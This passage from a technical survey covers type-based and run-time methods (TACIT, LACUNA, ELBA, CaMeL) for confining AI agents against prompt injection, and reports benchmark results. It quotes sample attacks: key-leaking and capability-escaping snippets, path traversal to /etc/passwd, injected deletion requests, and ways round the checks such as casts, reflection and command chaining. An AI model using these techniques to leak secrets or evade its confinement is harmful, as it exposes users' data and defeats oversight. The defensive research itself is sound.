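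Some of the original researchers later took a different approach in *Generative Compilation* (Mündler-Sasahara, Venev and colleagues, 2026), which uses the ordinary Rust compiler to check a program while the model is still writing it. The method closes the partial program's open brackets and fills its gaps with placeholders so that the compiler can process it. If the compiler reports an error, the model gets the message and can revise what it has written. For a small core of Rust, the researchers proved that the method never rejects a partial program that could still be completed. It needs no access to the model's probabilities, so it also works with commercial models.

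One study tested seven commercial and open models on translating C code into Rust and on writing code for recently changed libraries. For most combinations of model and task, compiler messages sent while the model was still writing led to fewer compile errors and more correct programs than messages sent after it had finished. So in 2026, compile errors still kept leading models from getting some answers right, at least in a strict language and on unfamiliar libraries.

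### Invented library features

Models also call functions that do not exist, or pass arguments that a function does not accept. A sound type checker with complete information about a library will always reject such a call, but Python's type checkers often work from incomplete descriptions of libraries.

*An Empirical Analysis of Static Analysis Methods for Detection and Mitigation* (Miranda-Pena, Reeson and colleagues, 2026) tested six models on Python tasks that require libraries. Between 8.1% and 40% of the models' answers used features that did not exist. The researchers then ran static analysis tools, which inspect code without executing it, including the type checkers Mypy and Pyright. Depending on the model and the set of tasks, the tools caught 16% to 70% of all errors and 14% to 85% of the invented features. Three of the models were GPT-3.5, GPT-4 and Claude 3, so the error rates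 are weak evidence about current models, but the tools' limits have probably changed less.

The higher detection rates include programs that were flagged for the wrong reason. The researchers examined 600 programs that had failed because of an invented feature and checked whether any warning concerned the actual problem. In the data science tasks, Mypy or Pyright flagged 57% of the programs, but only 38% for the right reason. In the two sets that were more varied, they flagged 19% and 23%, but only 4% and 10% for the right reason.

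False alarms were common. Only 16% of the GPT-4 data science answers that Mypy flagged contained an error, compared with 50% for Pyright. An agent that had to satisfy either tool before acting would often rewrite code that worked.

Miranda-Pena and colleagues also estimated that, of the 600 failures, a better static tool could catch 77% of those on the data science tasks and 70.5% and 48.5% of those in the other two sets. The tools they tested cannot catch, for example, a call in which the model passes a list of pairs to a function that picks random elements from a one-dimensional array. The library's type descriptions do not record the number of dimensions, so the tools accept the call.

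These ceilings partly reflect the tasks, however. In the two more varied sets, more than a third of the failures came from unclear instructions. For example, the model wrote code for one kind of table and the test used another. No analysis of the code alone can determine which kind the user meant.

Here, too, code that runs is often still wrong. The researchers asked another model, o3-mini, to repair the faulty programs using Pyright's report. For GPT-4's data science answers, the share that ran without an error rose from 76.8% to 82.1%, but the share that was correct rose only from 47.7% to 48.7%. o3-mini did slightly better on both measures without either type checker's report than with Pyright's.

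The programmer Simon Willison argues in *Hallucinations in code are the least dangerous form of LLM mistakes* (2025) that invented functions are a minor problem because running the code exposes them immediately, and that the real risk lies in mistakes that neither a compiler nor an interpreter reports. The counts above support the second claim. The first assumes that a trial run does no harm, which is true when a developer tests a program on a laptop. But an agent's snippet may issue a refund before it reaches the invented function, so a type checker can be valuable for agents even when it only catches mistakes that running the code would also reveal.

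### Typed and untyped languages

Coding agents might do better in typed languages if type checking catches some of their mistakes. GitHub's *Why AI is pushing developers toward typed languages* (2025) argues that they do, because types help AI fit new code into an existing project without breaking its assumptions. It also reports fast growth in typed languages, including more than 194% in a year for Luau, the scripting language of the game platform Roblox. These figures show which languages developers choose, but not whether their programs have fewer faults.

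The evidence on whether static types reduce bugs in human-written code is mixed. *To Type or Not to Type?* (Bogner, 2022) compared JavaScript projects on GitHub with projects in TypeScript, which adds static types to JavaScript. Bugs took slightly longer to fix in the TypeScript projects (an average of 33.0 days, compared with 31.9), and the paper concluded that TypeScript does not automatically lead to fewer bugs or easier fixes. Heavy use of `any`, which turns off type checking for a value, was associated with worse results on several measures of quality, but not with more bugs. Teams choose their own language, so differences between the projects may have nothing to do with types.

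In *Which Programming Language Is Best for Claude Code?* (March 2026), Endoh had Anthropic's coding agent build the same small version of the version-control program Git 20 times in each of 13 languages. Ruby, Python and JavaScript were the cheapest, at $0.36 to $0.39 per run. TypeScript cost $0.62, and Haskell, which has a strict type system, cost $0.74. Endoh, who helps develop Ruby, acknowledges a possible bias and lists other explanations for the differences, such as the larger amount of Python and JavaScript in models' training data.

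The clearest comparison is between Python with and without a type checker, because the language stays the same. When the agent also had to write type annotations and satisfy Mypy's strict mode, the average cost rose from $0.38 to $0.57 and the average time from 75 to 125 seconds. All the programs passed the tests in both conditions, so the type checker added cost and time without measurable gain.

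But the experiment could hardly have shown a gain from static types. The agent was given the tests and told to make them pass, and it succeeded in all but three of 600 runs. The experiment would have missed any type errors in code the tests did not run. The programs were also only a few hundred lines long, and Endoh accepts that static types may be worthwhile in larger projects.

The programmer Armin Ronacher likes typed languages but doubts that agents make good use of them. *In Support Of Shitty Types* (Ronacher, 2025) reports that adding type checks to an agent's work made the results worse. The agent would get the program running before it ran the type checker, which then found errors the agent had made much earlier. Fixing them used up much of its context (the limited amount of text a model can consider). Checking after every edit used even more context. The models also struggled with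 libraries that define very elaborate types, but they did well with Go, whose type system is simple and strictly enforced.

Ronacher gives no figures, and the observations date from August 2025, which is old for a claim about what models can understand. Late discovery of errors is a more general problem, which generative compilation tries to solve by reporting errors sooner. The problem also matters less for an agent that acts through short snippets, as in LACUNA, because the type checker reports a mistake before the model builds on it.

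## How can types limit what an action may touch?

A function of type `String => String` takes text and returns text. A function that shortens its input has this type, and so does one that posts the input to a website before shortening it. The type describes the input and output, but not what else the function does, so an ordinary type checker accepts the refund snippet that also sends off the customer's card number.

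The shop can keep a snippet from calling `cancelAccount` by leaving that tool out of the snippet's scope. But any Scala program can also open files and network connections through the standard library, whatever the developer intended. This power, which code has simply because it is running, is called ambient authority. The language must remove it before scope can fully limit what a snippet may touch.

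### Capabilities

Dennis and Van Horn (1965), in *Programming Semantics for Multiprogrammed Computations*, designed operations for computers that run several computations at once and must protect them from each other. Each computation has a list of capabilities for the things it may use. According to the book chapter *Early Capability Architectures*, a computation can start a subordinate one, copy a capability into the subordinate's list with chosen access rights, and later delete that capability from the list.

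Miller (2006), in *Robust Composition*, developed the idea for programming languages. Miller's concern was that separately written programs, combined so that they can cooperate, may damage each other instead. In the object-capability model, a capability is an ordinary program value, and code can cause an effect only if it holds the corresponding value. Odersky and colleagues give a small example:

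```
def writeOutput(fs: FileSystem^) =
  val f = fs.access("OUTPUT.md")
  f.write("The answer is 42.")
```

This function can write to the file only because its caller passed it `fs`. The file name "OUTPUT.md" is not enough, because the function cannot create a `FileSystem` itself. The value `f` is a narrower capability that gives access to only one file.

Passing capabilities around does not settle who has them, though, because a function can carry one inside it:

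```
val save = (s: String) => f.write(s)
```

Code that receives `save` can write to the file even if `f` is not in its scope. In ordinary Scala, `save` has the type `String => Unit`, where `Unit` means there is no useful result, and a function that does nothing has the same type. Older capability languages enforce their rules only while the program runs, so their compilers cannot distinguish the two functions.

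### Capabilities in types

Capture checking, an experimental feature of Scala 3, adds a capture set to each type, which lists the capabilities that a value of the type may use. For a function, the checker fills this set with the outside capabilities that the body uses. `save` uses `f` in its body, so its type becomes `String ->{f} Unit`.

| Type | Capabilities the function may use |
|---|---|
| `String -> Unit` | none |
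| `String ->{f} Unit` | `f` |
| `String ->{f, g} Unit` | `f` and `g` |
| `String => Unit` | any |

A function of the first type is pure. Each type in the table is a subtype of those below it, which means that a program can use a value of that type wherever it expects one of the lower types. Scala's *Capture Checking Basics* gives the general rule:

$$T_1^{\,C_1} <: T_2^{\,C_2} \quad \text{if} \quad C_1 <: C_2 \ \text{ and } \ T_1 <: T_2$$

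Here $T^{\,C}$ is the type $T$ with capture set $C$, and $<:$ means "is a subtype of". When $<:$ relates two capture sets, it means that the second accounts for everything in the first. A program can therefore use a function wherever it allows more than the function captures, but it cannot use `save` where it requires a pure function.

The checker still tracks a capability when another object wraps it. If a logger `l` writes through the file system `fs`, its type is `Logger^{fs}`, so even a function that only writes log messages isn't pure. The checker also counts any capability the code may use, even if the code never uses it. A function that writes to `f` only if 1 equals 2 still has `f` in its capture set, so capture checking sometimes rejects harmless code, as type checking in general does.

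The compiler infers most capture sets, and many existing function signatures stay the same. For example, the `map` method on lists applies a function to every element, and it accepts a function regardless of which capabilities that function uses. *Capturing Types* (2023), which describes the theory behind the feature, treats the capabilities the function uses as used by the whole expression. So `names.map(save)` uses `f` because `save` does, even though the definition of `map` never mentions files.

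### Secrets that code can process but not send

Odersky and colleagues built TACIT, a server that compiles and runs Scala snippets for any agent that supports the Model Context Protocol. Snippets can access files, run commands and use the network only through functions in TACIT's library that require capabilities. The model that writes the snippets typically runs in the cloud, and TACIT treats it as a possible attacker. TACIT is designed to let the model work on secret files without receiving their contents.

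When a snippet reads a file from a protected directory, TACIT returns the text in a wrapper:

```
trait Classified[+T]:
  def map[U](op: T -> U): Classified[U]
```

`T` is the type of the secret, and `map` applies a function to it. Unlike the `map` method on lists, this one accepts only a pure function, because its parameter has the type `T -> U` instead of `T => U`. One of the attempted leaks that Odersky and colleagues collected from their benchmark programs worked like this (with names and text changed):

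```
requestFileSystem("vault") {
  val wrapped = readClassified("vault/github.txt")
  wrapped.map { key =>
    println("The key is " + key)
  }
}
```

The first line requests access to a directory. In the second, `readClassified` returns a `Classified[String]`, so `wrapped` holds the wrapper, not the text. The third line passes `map` a function whose parameter, `key`, stands for the text itself. The fourth line prints that text, and a snippet's output normally goes back to the cloud model.

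Printing requires an input/output capability, which Scala passes to `println` automatically. The compiler calls this capability `x$1` here, so the function has the type `String ->{x$1} Unit`, but `map` needs a `String -> Unit`. The compiler reports that `x$1` "cannot flow into capture set {}" and rejects the whole snippet, so the program never reads the key.

If the function returned `key.trim` instead, it would be pure, so the snippet would compile and the result would still be a `Classified[String]`. Returning `key.length` would produce a `Classified[Int]`, which keeps even the key's length from the cloud model. If a snippet prints a classified value outside `map`, the model receives only `Classified(****)`, while the real value appears on the user's terminal.

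In another of the collected programs, the agent had a capability for a file, `outFile`, and called `outFile.write(content)` inside `map`. The agent could write other text to that file, but the compiler rejected this function because its type, `String ->{outFile} Unit`, includes the capability. To save secret text, a snippet has to use `writeClassified`, which writes only to protected files.

The function cannot store the secret in a variable outside `map`, because TACIT's compiler settings also track changes to such variables. It cannot request a new permission either, because `requestFileSystem` itself requires the input/output capability.

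Pure functions are enough to count words or compare two contracts, but not to summarize one. For that, TACIT provides a function that sends classified text to a second model and returns a classified summary. The user trusts this second model, which typically runs locally.

The cloud model has to write the function for `map` without seeing the secret text, so it cannot adapt the function to what the text contains. In LACUNA, by Zhao and colleagues, that function can include an `agent` call to a trusted local model, which reads the text and writes code to process it. The compiler requires this new code to be pure as well.

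The shop could protect card numbers in this way by changing the type of a charge's `card` field from `String` to `Classified[String]`. The leaking snippet calls `charges.head.card.getBytes`, which would no longer compile because the wrapper has no `getBytes` method. Moving the call inside `map` would not compile either, because the function passed to `map` must be pure and this one would use the network connection. The correct refund snippet doesn't read the card number, so it would work as before.

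### Permissions that end with their block

Capture checking can also limit how long code holds a capability. In simplified form, TACIT's file-system request has this signature:

```
def requestFileSystem[T](root: String)(block: FileSystem^ => T): T
```

The function creates a capability for the directory `root`, passes it to a block of code, and returns the block's result, which can have any type `T`. The capability is supposed to expire at that point. A snippet might try to keep it by returning a function that uses it later:

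```
val bad = requestFileSystem("/data") { fs =>
  () => fs.access("secret.txt").read()
}
bad()
```

The inner function takes no arguments and reads the file when something calls it, which here happens on the last line, after the block has ended. The compiler finds the problem as follows:

1. The caret in `FileSystem^` marks `fs` as a capability that the compiler must track.
2. The inner function uses `fs`, so its type is `() ->{fs} String`.
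3. This function is the result of the block, so `T` would have to be the same type.
4. The variable `bad` would then have that type too. But `bad` is outside the block, where `fs` does not exist, and a capture set may contain only capabilities that are visible where the set appears.

No type fits, so the snippet does not compile. Scala can sometimes replace an invisible capability with a visible one that covers it. For example, it can replace a local logger with the file system the logger writes to. SoftwareMill's *Understanding Capture Checking in Scala* explains that this fails for a parameter like `fs` because the compiler has no information about which capabilities lie behind it, and so has nothing to replace it with.

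The compiler accepts a block that reads the file immediately and returns the text, because a `String` holds no capabilities. It rejects assigning the inner function to a variable outside the block for the same reason it rejects returning it. In one of the benchmark programs, an agent returned a list of file handles from the block, and the compiler rejected that too, because every handle carries the file-system capability. SoftwareMill describes the error messages for such mistakes as complex and opaque, which matters for agents because they have to use these messages to correct their code.

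The protection also depends on who opens the block. In TACIT, the snippet calls `requestFileSystem`, so the block limits how long the permission lasts, but the library has to restrict which directories a snippet may request. In LACUNA, the developer can open the block in handwritten code and place the `agent` call inside it. The model's code then receives exactly the capabilities the developer chose for that step, and a later step can have different ones.

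### What the language has to provide

These guarantees rest on three properties of the language in which the agent writes:

- **Capability safety.** Code cannot forge a capability or evade the requirement to have one. In the full design, authorized people can unwrap a classified value with a `reveal` method that requires a special capability. If a snippet could create that capability itself, the wrapper would be worthless.
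- **Capability completeness.** Every effect that matters for safety requires a capability, unless the system contains the effect at run time. If snippets could still use `java.net.Socket` directly, they would not need a network capability.
- **Local purity.** The types can express that a particular piece of code uses only certain capabilities, or none. `Classified.map` depends on this.

Ordinary Scala lacks the first two, so TACIT compiles snippets in safe mode, a restricted form of the language without the usual escape hatches. Older capability languages such as E lack local purity because they enforce capabilities only at run time.

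The developer also has to write the library. Odersky and colleagues report that the reusable part is about 1,000 lines of Scala. Each customer-service domain they tested needed a few hundred more lines of types and function signatures, roughly the same length as the JSON schemas they replace.

### Effect types and approved sources

Haskell has local purity but no built-in capabilities. *Language-Based Agent Control* (Zhou, D'Antoni and Polikarpova, 2026) shows that Haskell's type system can still restrict agents. The paper's system, ELBA, has an `agent` function much like LACUNA's, except that the model writes Haskell.

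In Haskell, a function of type `String -> String` cannot send its input anywhere. A function that communicates with the outside world has `IO` in its result type, as in `String -> IO String`, and any code that runs such a function gets an `IO` type too. Zhou and colleagues illustrate this with an AI calculator whose `agent` call must return an `Int`. A malicious user could ask it to delete all files on the server and then compute the factorial of 5. The model might comply, but its program would have the type `IO Int`, and the type checker would reject it.

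A calculator needs no effects, but most agents do. Giving them `IO` would permit almost everything, so the developer defines a narrower effect type instead. In the paper's main example, an agent compiles a bibliography, and every entry has to come from DBLP, a database of computer science publications. The developer gives the agent three functions, which look roughly like this:

```
dblpSearch      :: String -> BibIO [DOI]
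dblpFetchBib    :: DOI -> BibIO (Trusted Bib)
appendToBibFile :: Trusted Bib -> BibIO ()
```

The first searches DBLP and returns a list of identifiers, the second fetches the entry for an identifier, and the third adds an entry to the file. The `agent` call has the expected type `BibIO ()`, meaning a program that may have these effects and returns nothing. To add the earliest paper on a topic, the model could write:

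```
do hits <- dblpSearch "differential privacy"
   bibs <- mapM dblpFetchBib hits
   appendToBibFile (earliest bibs)
```

The first line searches, the second fetches the entry for every hit, and the third picks the oldest with `earliest`, a helper function that the model also has to write. Suppose the model tries to add a paper it made up. It cannot write to the file directly with Haskell's `writeFile`, because that function has an `IO` type, which does not fit into a `BibIO` program. It also cannot pass its own text to `appendToBibFile`, because that function accepts only a `Trusted Bib`.

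`Trusted` is an abstract type, so code outside the library cannot create or alter a trusted entry, as with a `Charge` whose constructor is private. It can only get one from `dblpFetchBib`. An abstract type alone would leave `writeFile` available, and an effect type alone would let the agent add invented entries through `appendToBibFile`.

A developer could get the same guarantee without types by offering a single tool that fetches an entry and immediately writes it to the file. But then the agent could not sort or filter entries in code, and the model would have to read them one at a time.

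Zhou and colleagues compared ELBA with a conventional agent on 100 bibliography tasks, using Claude Sonnet 5 for both. The conventional agent got the authors, year or DOI wrong in 19 of 1,002 citations, and ELBA in none of 925. The conventional agent had a web search tool and wrote the citations itself, so part of the difference may come from ELBA's use of DBLP rather than from its types. The types ensure that ELBA's agent cannot bypass DBLP, but not that the papers suit the topic.

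If the model's code calls `agent` again inside a `BibIO` program, the new call must produce either another `BibIO` program or one with a stricter type, such as a type that permits no effects.

Zhou and colleagues prove a general version of this. They describe a program's behavior by its traces, the sequences of observable tool calls that it can make. A type $t$ enforces a property $P$ if, for every program $e$ in the language,

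$$\vdash e : t \ \implies\ P(\mathrm{traces}(e)).$$

The theorem is that any such property still holds when `agent` calls are added, provided that every generated program passes the type checker before it runs. The proof makes no assumption about what the model writes. It replaces each `agent` call with an ordinary function that queries the model, checks the reply and evaluates it. The result is an ordinary well-typed program, so $P$ holds for it, and because it has the same traces as the original program, $P$ holds for the original too. Generated code may contain further `agent` calls, so the proof uses induction on the depth of nesting.

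### What the program still checks while running

Some limits depend on actual values, which a type checker does not know. TACIT and ELBA leave these to checks at run time.

| Condition | System | When the check happens |
|---|---|---|
| Only pure functions process classified data | TACIT | Before the snippet runs |
| A file-system capability stays inside its block | TACIT | Before the snippet runs |
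| Every bibliography entry comes from DBLP | ELBA | Before the snippet runs |
| A file lies inside the permitted directory | Both | During the run |
| A host or command is on the permitted list | TACIT | During the run |
| The labels on data allow it to reach a recipient | ELBA | During the run |

File paths need checks at both compile time and run time. In ELBA's file library, `readRIO "/etc/passwd"` does not compile because `readRIO` requires a `Path`, another abstract type, rather than a `String`. The program receives a `Path` for one directory and can derive others from it, as in `root // "input.txt"`. But the text after the slashes might be `../../etc/passwd`, or the name of a link to a file elsewhere on the disk. So the `//` operator resolves the real location at run time and rejects anything outside the original directory. TACIT also raises an exception if a snippet tries to access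 a file outside its directory.

TACIT also has to handle exceptions at run time. A function inside `Classified.map` could raise an error whose message contains the secret. According to Scala's *Safe Mode*, a type system that tracked all exceptions would be too cumbersome, because even a division by zero can cause one. TACIT therefore catches the exception and keeps its message from the agent.

ELBA's information-flow control works entirely at run time. Information-flow control governs where data may travel inside a program, rather than who may read it first. ELBA uses an existing Haskell library, LIO, which keeps a label recording how confidential the data read so far is and which sources have influenced the running computation. In the paper's example, a program downloads text from phony.com and then tries to send it to the user. The download marks the computation as influenced by phony.com.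 The policy does not allow that source to influence messages to the user, so LIO stops the program with an error when it tries to send the text.

An error from LIO can occur halfway through a program, after earlier lines have already had their effects. ELBA asks the model for new code only after type errors, when no tool has run yet.

A developer can also put a run-time check inside a tool. Scala's documentation sketches an email tool that shows each message to the user and sends it only after approval. The agent cannot skip this step, because it has no other way to send email.

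### Sandboxes and run-time tracking

Many coding agents run their code in a sandbox, which restricts a whole process to certain directories and network addresses. Suppose an agent has to work on a private contract with the help of a cloud model. It needs to read the file and connect to the model. A sandbox that permits both operations also permits the agent to send the contract to the model, and blocking either one would stop the agent from doing its work. TACIT permits both operations but prevents the contract's contents from reaching the model.

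Sandboxes have the advantage of working for programs in any language. If a snippet starts an external program, capture checking does not apply to what that program does. Odersky and colleagues recommend using both.

Some agents also compare shell commands with lists of permitted or forbidden patterns. Zhou and colleagues consider these checks brittle. In March 2026, a fault in Claude Code let later commands in a chain bypass the rules because the software checked only the first one. A rule that forbids reading a file also has no effect if the command starts Python and the Python code opens the file.

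CaMeL (Debenedetti et al., 2025) does track data from one operation to the next, but at run time. As Odersky et al. and Zhou et al. describe it, one model writes the whole program before it sees any data, and a second model extracts information from untrusted text. A custom interpreter runs the program and marks values by their origin, so that it can block a tool call that would use them improperly. A malicious message to the shop could influence the program's values, but it could not add a call to `cancelAccount`, because the program already exists when the message arrives.

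Because of this separation, the program cannot adapt if the customer's message describes a second problem. TACIT and ELBA, by contrast, let the agent read a result and then write more code.

Odersky and colleagues also object that CaMeL's interpreter accepts only part of Python, without recursion or functions defined by the program. Working out all data flows precisely in unrestricted code can take a compiler exponential time. Capture checking avoids this because each function's type lists the capabilities it may use, so the checker can examine one function at a time. They further object that CaMeL's marks disappear once a value enters a model's conversation as ordinary text. In TACIT, classified text stays in its wrapper and so never enters the conversation.

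But TACIT protects only data that the developer has wrapped, while CaMeL tracks every value in the program. If the shop's agent reads a customer's message as ordinary text, the message may cause it to refund the wrong charge, and TACIT will allow this because the agent is authorized to issue refunds. The developer can reduce this risk by wrapping untrusted text as well as secrets. When Odersky and colleagues adapted a set of email, banking and travel tasks to TACIT, they made emails, web pages and hotel reviews `Classified`, so that the agent could process them without reading them.

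## How well have these limits held, and what do they rest on?

Experiments have tested the authority guarantee both with attacks that a model may or may not fall for and with simulated attacks that always take over part of the agent.

Odersky and colleagues tested TACIT on a small Scala project with a protected directory that held API keys, a database and confidential documents. An untrusted cloud model carried out the tasks, and a trusted local model could process the protected text. There were 131 trials per model. In 120 of them, the researchers combined 12 ordinary tasks, such as summarizing a confidential incident report, with ten prompt injections of increasing sophistication. In the other 11, the user was the attacker, who asked for secrets outright in five trials and gave a false reason, such as an emergency, in six.

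Each trial ran once with the secrets in the `Classified` wrapper and once with them as plain strings. A trial counted as safe if no secret appeared in the agent's output. The last column shows how often the agent also completed the ordinary task correctly.

| Model | Secrets | Safe against injections (of 120) | Safe against malicious users (of 11) | Safe overall | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|---|---|
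| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Wrapped | 120 | 11 | 100% | 99.2% |
| Claude Sonnet 4.6 | Plain | 120 | 9 | 98.5% | 83.3% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Wrapped | 120 | 11 | 100% | 90.0% |
| MiniMax M2.5 | Plain | 117 | 3 | 91.6% | 88.3% |

The overall percentages understate the difference the wrapper made, because most trials were injections that both models usually resisted even without it. When the user was the attacker, MiniMax M2.5 revealed secrets in 8 of 11 trials without the wrapper and in none with it.

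The wrapper did not reduce the number of completed tasks. Sonnet completed more with it, though Odersky and colleagues suspect this was an artifact of their setup. Without the wrapper, Sonnet often ran out of time or turns, and it sometimes stopped to warn the user about an injection instead of finishing the task.

On their own, 131 safe trials in a row are compatible with a failure rate of up to about 2%. The argument for a stronger claim is that the cloud model never receives the secret, so it cannot be persuaded to reveal it. The trials mainly test whether the software implements this mechanism correctly and whether agents can still get work done under it.

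### Attacks planted in tool results

AgentDojo is a public benchmark that plants injections in the data an agent's tools return. Its tasks cover banking, travel, office work and the messaging service Slack. Odersky and colleagues adapted it to TACIT, and Zhao and colleagues adapted it to LACUNA. Both papers compare their results with published figures for CaMeL, which tracks data at run time. The last column gives the lowest and highest completion rates across the four domains.

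| Model | System | Successful attacks | Tasks completed |
|---|---|---|---|
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | CaMeL | 0 | 1.4–53.8% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | TACIT | 0 | 40.0–64.3% |
| Gemini 2.5 Pro | LACUNA | 7 | 42.9–63.6% |
| o4-mini-high | CaMeL | 1 | 62.5–81.4% |
| o4-mini-high | TACIT | 1 | 47.6–68.6% |
| o4-mini-high | LACUNA | 1 | 49.5–71.4% |

The two papers give different numbers of trials. Odersky and colleagues list 574 for office work, which gives 963 per model. Zhao and colleagues list 560, which gives 949, even where they repeat TACIT's results. Both papers report the same counts of successful attacks, and the eight that succeeded against LACUNA are about 0.4% of its trials using either total.

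TACIT's one counted failure occurred in a travel task. The user asked the agent to book a particular hotel, whose reviews included a recommendation for a different hotel planted by the attacker. The agent booked the right hotel but quoted the reviews to the user, including the planted text. Odersky and colleagues attribute the failure to AgentDojo's scoring rule, which is based on whether the other hotel's name appears in the output. That is a fair account of the booking, and the policy allowed public reviews to reach the user, but the attacker still got an advertisement in front of the user.

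Zhao and colleagues present LACUNA's eight cases as consistent with a limit of their guarantee, which does not stop an attacker from steering the model into misusing a capability it needs for its task. They do not attribute the cases to the scoring.

With o4-mini-high, CaMeL completed more tasks than TACIT in every domain. In office work, CaMeL completed 81.4% of tasks and TACIT completed 52.9%. Odersky and colleagues nevertheless describe TACIT's completion rates as comparable to CaMeL's.

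These results also lack a baseline without protection, so they do not show how many attacks the systems stopped. With newer models, that number could be zero. When Zhou and colleagues ran AgentDojo's Slack tasks with Claude Opus 4.7, Opus 4.8, Sonnet 5 and GPT 5.4, all four models resisted every standard attack, even with ELBA's policies switched off.

### Attacks that always succeed

If every model passes a test without protection, the test shows little about the protection. It also doesn't show that the models are safe, because real attackers adapt. Zhou and colleagues note that GPT-Red, OpenAI's automated attack system, consistently got past GPT-5.5's defenses. They therefore simulated an injection that always works.

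In ELBA, an agent reads data by passing it to a sub-agent together with a task. For this experiment, the researchers changed the software so that whenever the data contained a planted instruction, the sub-agent received the data without its real task. The sub-agent then carried out the attacker's instruction as if it were its own assignment. The researchers ran each of the 105 combinations of task and injection seven times, for a total of 735 trials per model.

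| Model | Injections resisted, with policies | Injections resisted, without | Tasks completed, with policies | Tasks completed, without |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Opus 4.7 | 735 | 425 | 351 | 523 |
| Opus 4.8 | 735 | 460 | 312 | 557 |
| GPT 5.4 | 735 | 621 | 338 | 558 |
| Sonnet 5 | 735 | 540 | 294 | 494 |

Between 16% and 42% of the injections achieved their goal without policies, and none did with them, although the zero depends on a manual correction. AgentDojo's scoring counted 29 of the 2,940 runs as successful attacks because the agent had opened a certain web address. The researchers reviewed all 29 and found no violation, since merely opening the address revealed nothing. The policies would have blocked a request that carried private data, or one made after the agent had read any.

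This result depends on run-time checks as well as type checking. The type checker only stops the agent's code from bypassing LIO when it uses Slack. LIO checks the data's labels at run time, and without those checks, well-typed code could still send data to the wrong person.

### What the limits cost

The policies also blocked legitimate work. Under attack, the models completed 494 to 558 tasks without policies and 294 to 351 with them. When there was no attack, they completed 14 to 18 of the 21 Slack tasks without policies and 8 to 10 with them.

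The reason is the policy that Zhou and colleagues chose, which lowers a model's privileges to those of the data's source when the model reads untrusted data. This stops a malicious web page from making the agent send messages, but it can also block a user's request to read a harmless page and tell colleagues about it. CaMeL completed even fewer tasks under its policies, 4 to 6 of the 21.

Type errors account for very little of the loss. In the ordinary AgentDojo runs, ELBA requested corrected code an average of 0.13 times per run, and the model failed to produce a well-typed program within the allowed attempts in only 0.26% of runs.

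Other experiments measured more directly how writing typed code affects task success, with mixed results. On τ²-bench, the customer-service benchmark, Odersky and colleagues compared TACIT with standard tool calls for three models in two domains. Agents that wrote typed Scala solved 0.8 to 3.7 percentage points more tasks. On SWE-bench Lite, which asks agents to fix real software bugs, the one model they tested solved 41.7% with TACIT and 43.3% without.

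LACUNA did worse on τ²-bench, where, with deepseek-v4-flash, it solved 76% of 392 tasks and the standard agent solved 90%. That 14-point gap is considerable, and it was 22 points in the retail domain, though Zhao and colleagues call the overall result "on par". The model has more to do in LACUNA, because it has to write the control flow of the whole task in Scala as well as the individual actions.

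A strict policy can be worth using despite its drawbacks if there is a sensible way to handle the actions it blocks. Zhou and colleagues suggest using it as a conservative filter, where actions that satisfy the policy go ahead automatically and a person decides about the rest.

### The software that has to be right

A type checker can keep an untrusted model within limits only if other parts of the system work correctly. In TACIT, these are the Scala compiler, the software that runs the compiled code, the library that provides capabilities, and the local model, if there is one. In LACUNA, they include the developer's own program, because it determines what is in scope.

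The compiler is the least settled of these. Researchers have produced computer-checkable proofs that the core type system behind capture checking is sound. But Odersky and colleagues say a further argument is needed to show that safe mode, the restricted form of Scala in which TACIT compiles snippets, has its intended properties. A proof about a type system also does not rule out bugs in the compiler that implements it. Scala's documentation for version 3.7.2 describes capture checking as "highly experimental and unstable". According to the software company VirtusLab, safe mode is available only in nightly builds, the development versions of the compiler.

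ELBA builds on older components, and LIO has published soundness proofs. But the theorem by Zhou and colleagues only carries over to model-written code the properties that the host language already enforces. A flaw in the compiler or a library that breaks a property for code written by people also breaks that property for code written by models.

Library authors can also make mistakes that the compiler will not catch. Some harmless library code needs features that safe mode forbids. Scala's documentation gives the example of a class that caches a function's results in a variable the compiler does not track. This is safe as long as the variable holds only earlier results and the function always returns the same result for the same input. After checking this, the programmer marks the class `@assumeSafe`, and the compiler lets snippets use it.

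The compiler does not verify the claim. If the shop's developer put this mark on a logging function that writes messages to a shared file without requiring a capability, the compiler would treat calls to that function as pure. A snippet could then call it inside `map` to log a customer's card number, and a later snippet could read the log.

The local model requires similar trust. Its type shows that calling it requires no capability, so the compiler allows the call inside `map`. But the type cannot show that the service behind the call discards the text afterwards. If the service kept one request as context for the next, a secret could appear in an unwrapped answer.

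### Closing the escape hatches

Ordinary Scala has many features that would let a snippet evade capture checking. The simplest is a cast, which tells the compiler to treat a value as having a different type. `Classified.map` normally rejects the file-writing function `save` because its type, `String ->{f} Unit`, is not pure. But Scala's library of unsafe features includes a cast that removes the capture set from a type. That cast would give `save` the type `String -> Unit`, so `map` would accept it even though it would still write to the file.

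Safe mode blocks this cast and several other routes:

| Safe mode forbids | What a snippet could otherwise do |
|---|---|
| Unchecked casts and pattern matches | Give a function a type that omits its capabilities |
| The `caps.unsafe` module | Remove a capture set directly |
| `@unchecked` annotations | Turn off a compiler check at one point in the code |
| Reflection | Find and call methods by name at run time, out of the checker's sight |
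| Global objects that are not themselves safe | Cause effects through libraries that do not require capabilities |

Safe mode also requires capture checking, including the tracking of changes to variables. The rule in the last row of the table blocks the refund snippet that sends a card number through `java.net.Socket`, because that class is not in the part of the standard library that safe mode permits. VirtusLab points out that a snippet also cannot mark its own code `@assumeSafe`.

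However, the restriction on libraries covers only global objects. A capability that the developer passes to a snippet can come from any code. According to Scala's documentation, the designer of that capability is responsible for exposing only suitable functions. If the shop gives a snippet an ordinary web client, the snippet can do everything the client can.

Haskell needs the same restriction, because its function `unsafePerformIO` hides an effect inside an expression typed as pure. The AI calculator could still use it to delete files. A compiler setting called Safe Haskell excludes such functions.

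Safe mode is recommended but optional in LACUNA. Without it, a snippet that holds no capability can still use reflection or launch another program, and Zhao and colleagues say that developers must then treat the snippet as ordinary untrusted code.

### Why TypeScript gives weaker assurance

TypeScript would be a convenient language for agents, since models have seen a great deal of it. But its type system is unsound by design. Consider a TypeScript version of the shop's tools:

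```
const charges: Charge[] = [];
refund(charges[0], 500);
```

The list is empty, so `charges[0]` is `undefined`, JavaScript's value for something missing. With its usual settings, the compiler still gives this expression the type `Charge` and accepts the program, which then calls `refund` with `undefined`. In Scala, asking for the first element of an empty list raises an exception, so `refund` is never called.

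TypeScript also lets programmers bypass type checking with a single word or character. The compiler accepts a value of type `any` anywhere. The keyword `as` asserts that a value has a certain type, and an exclamation mark asserts that a value is not missing. The compiler accepts these assertions with little checking, and the running program does not check them either.

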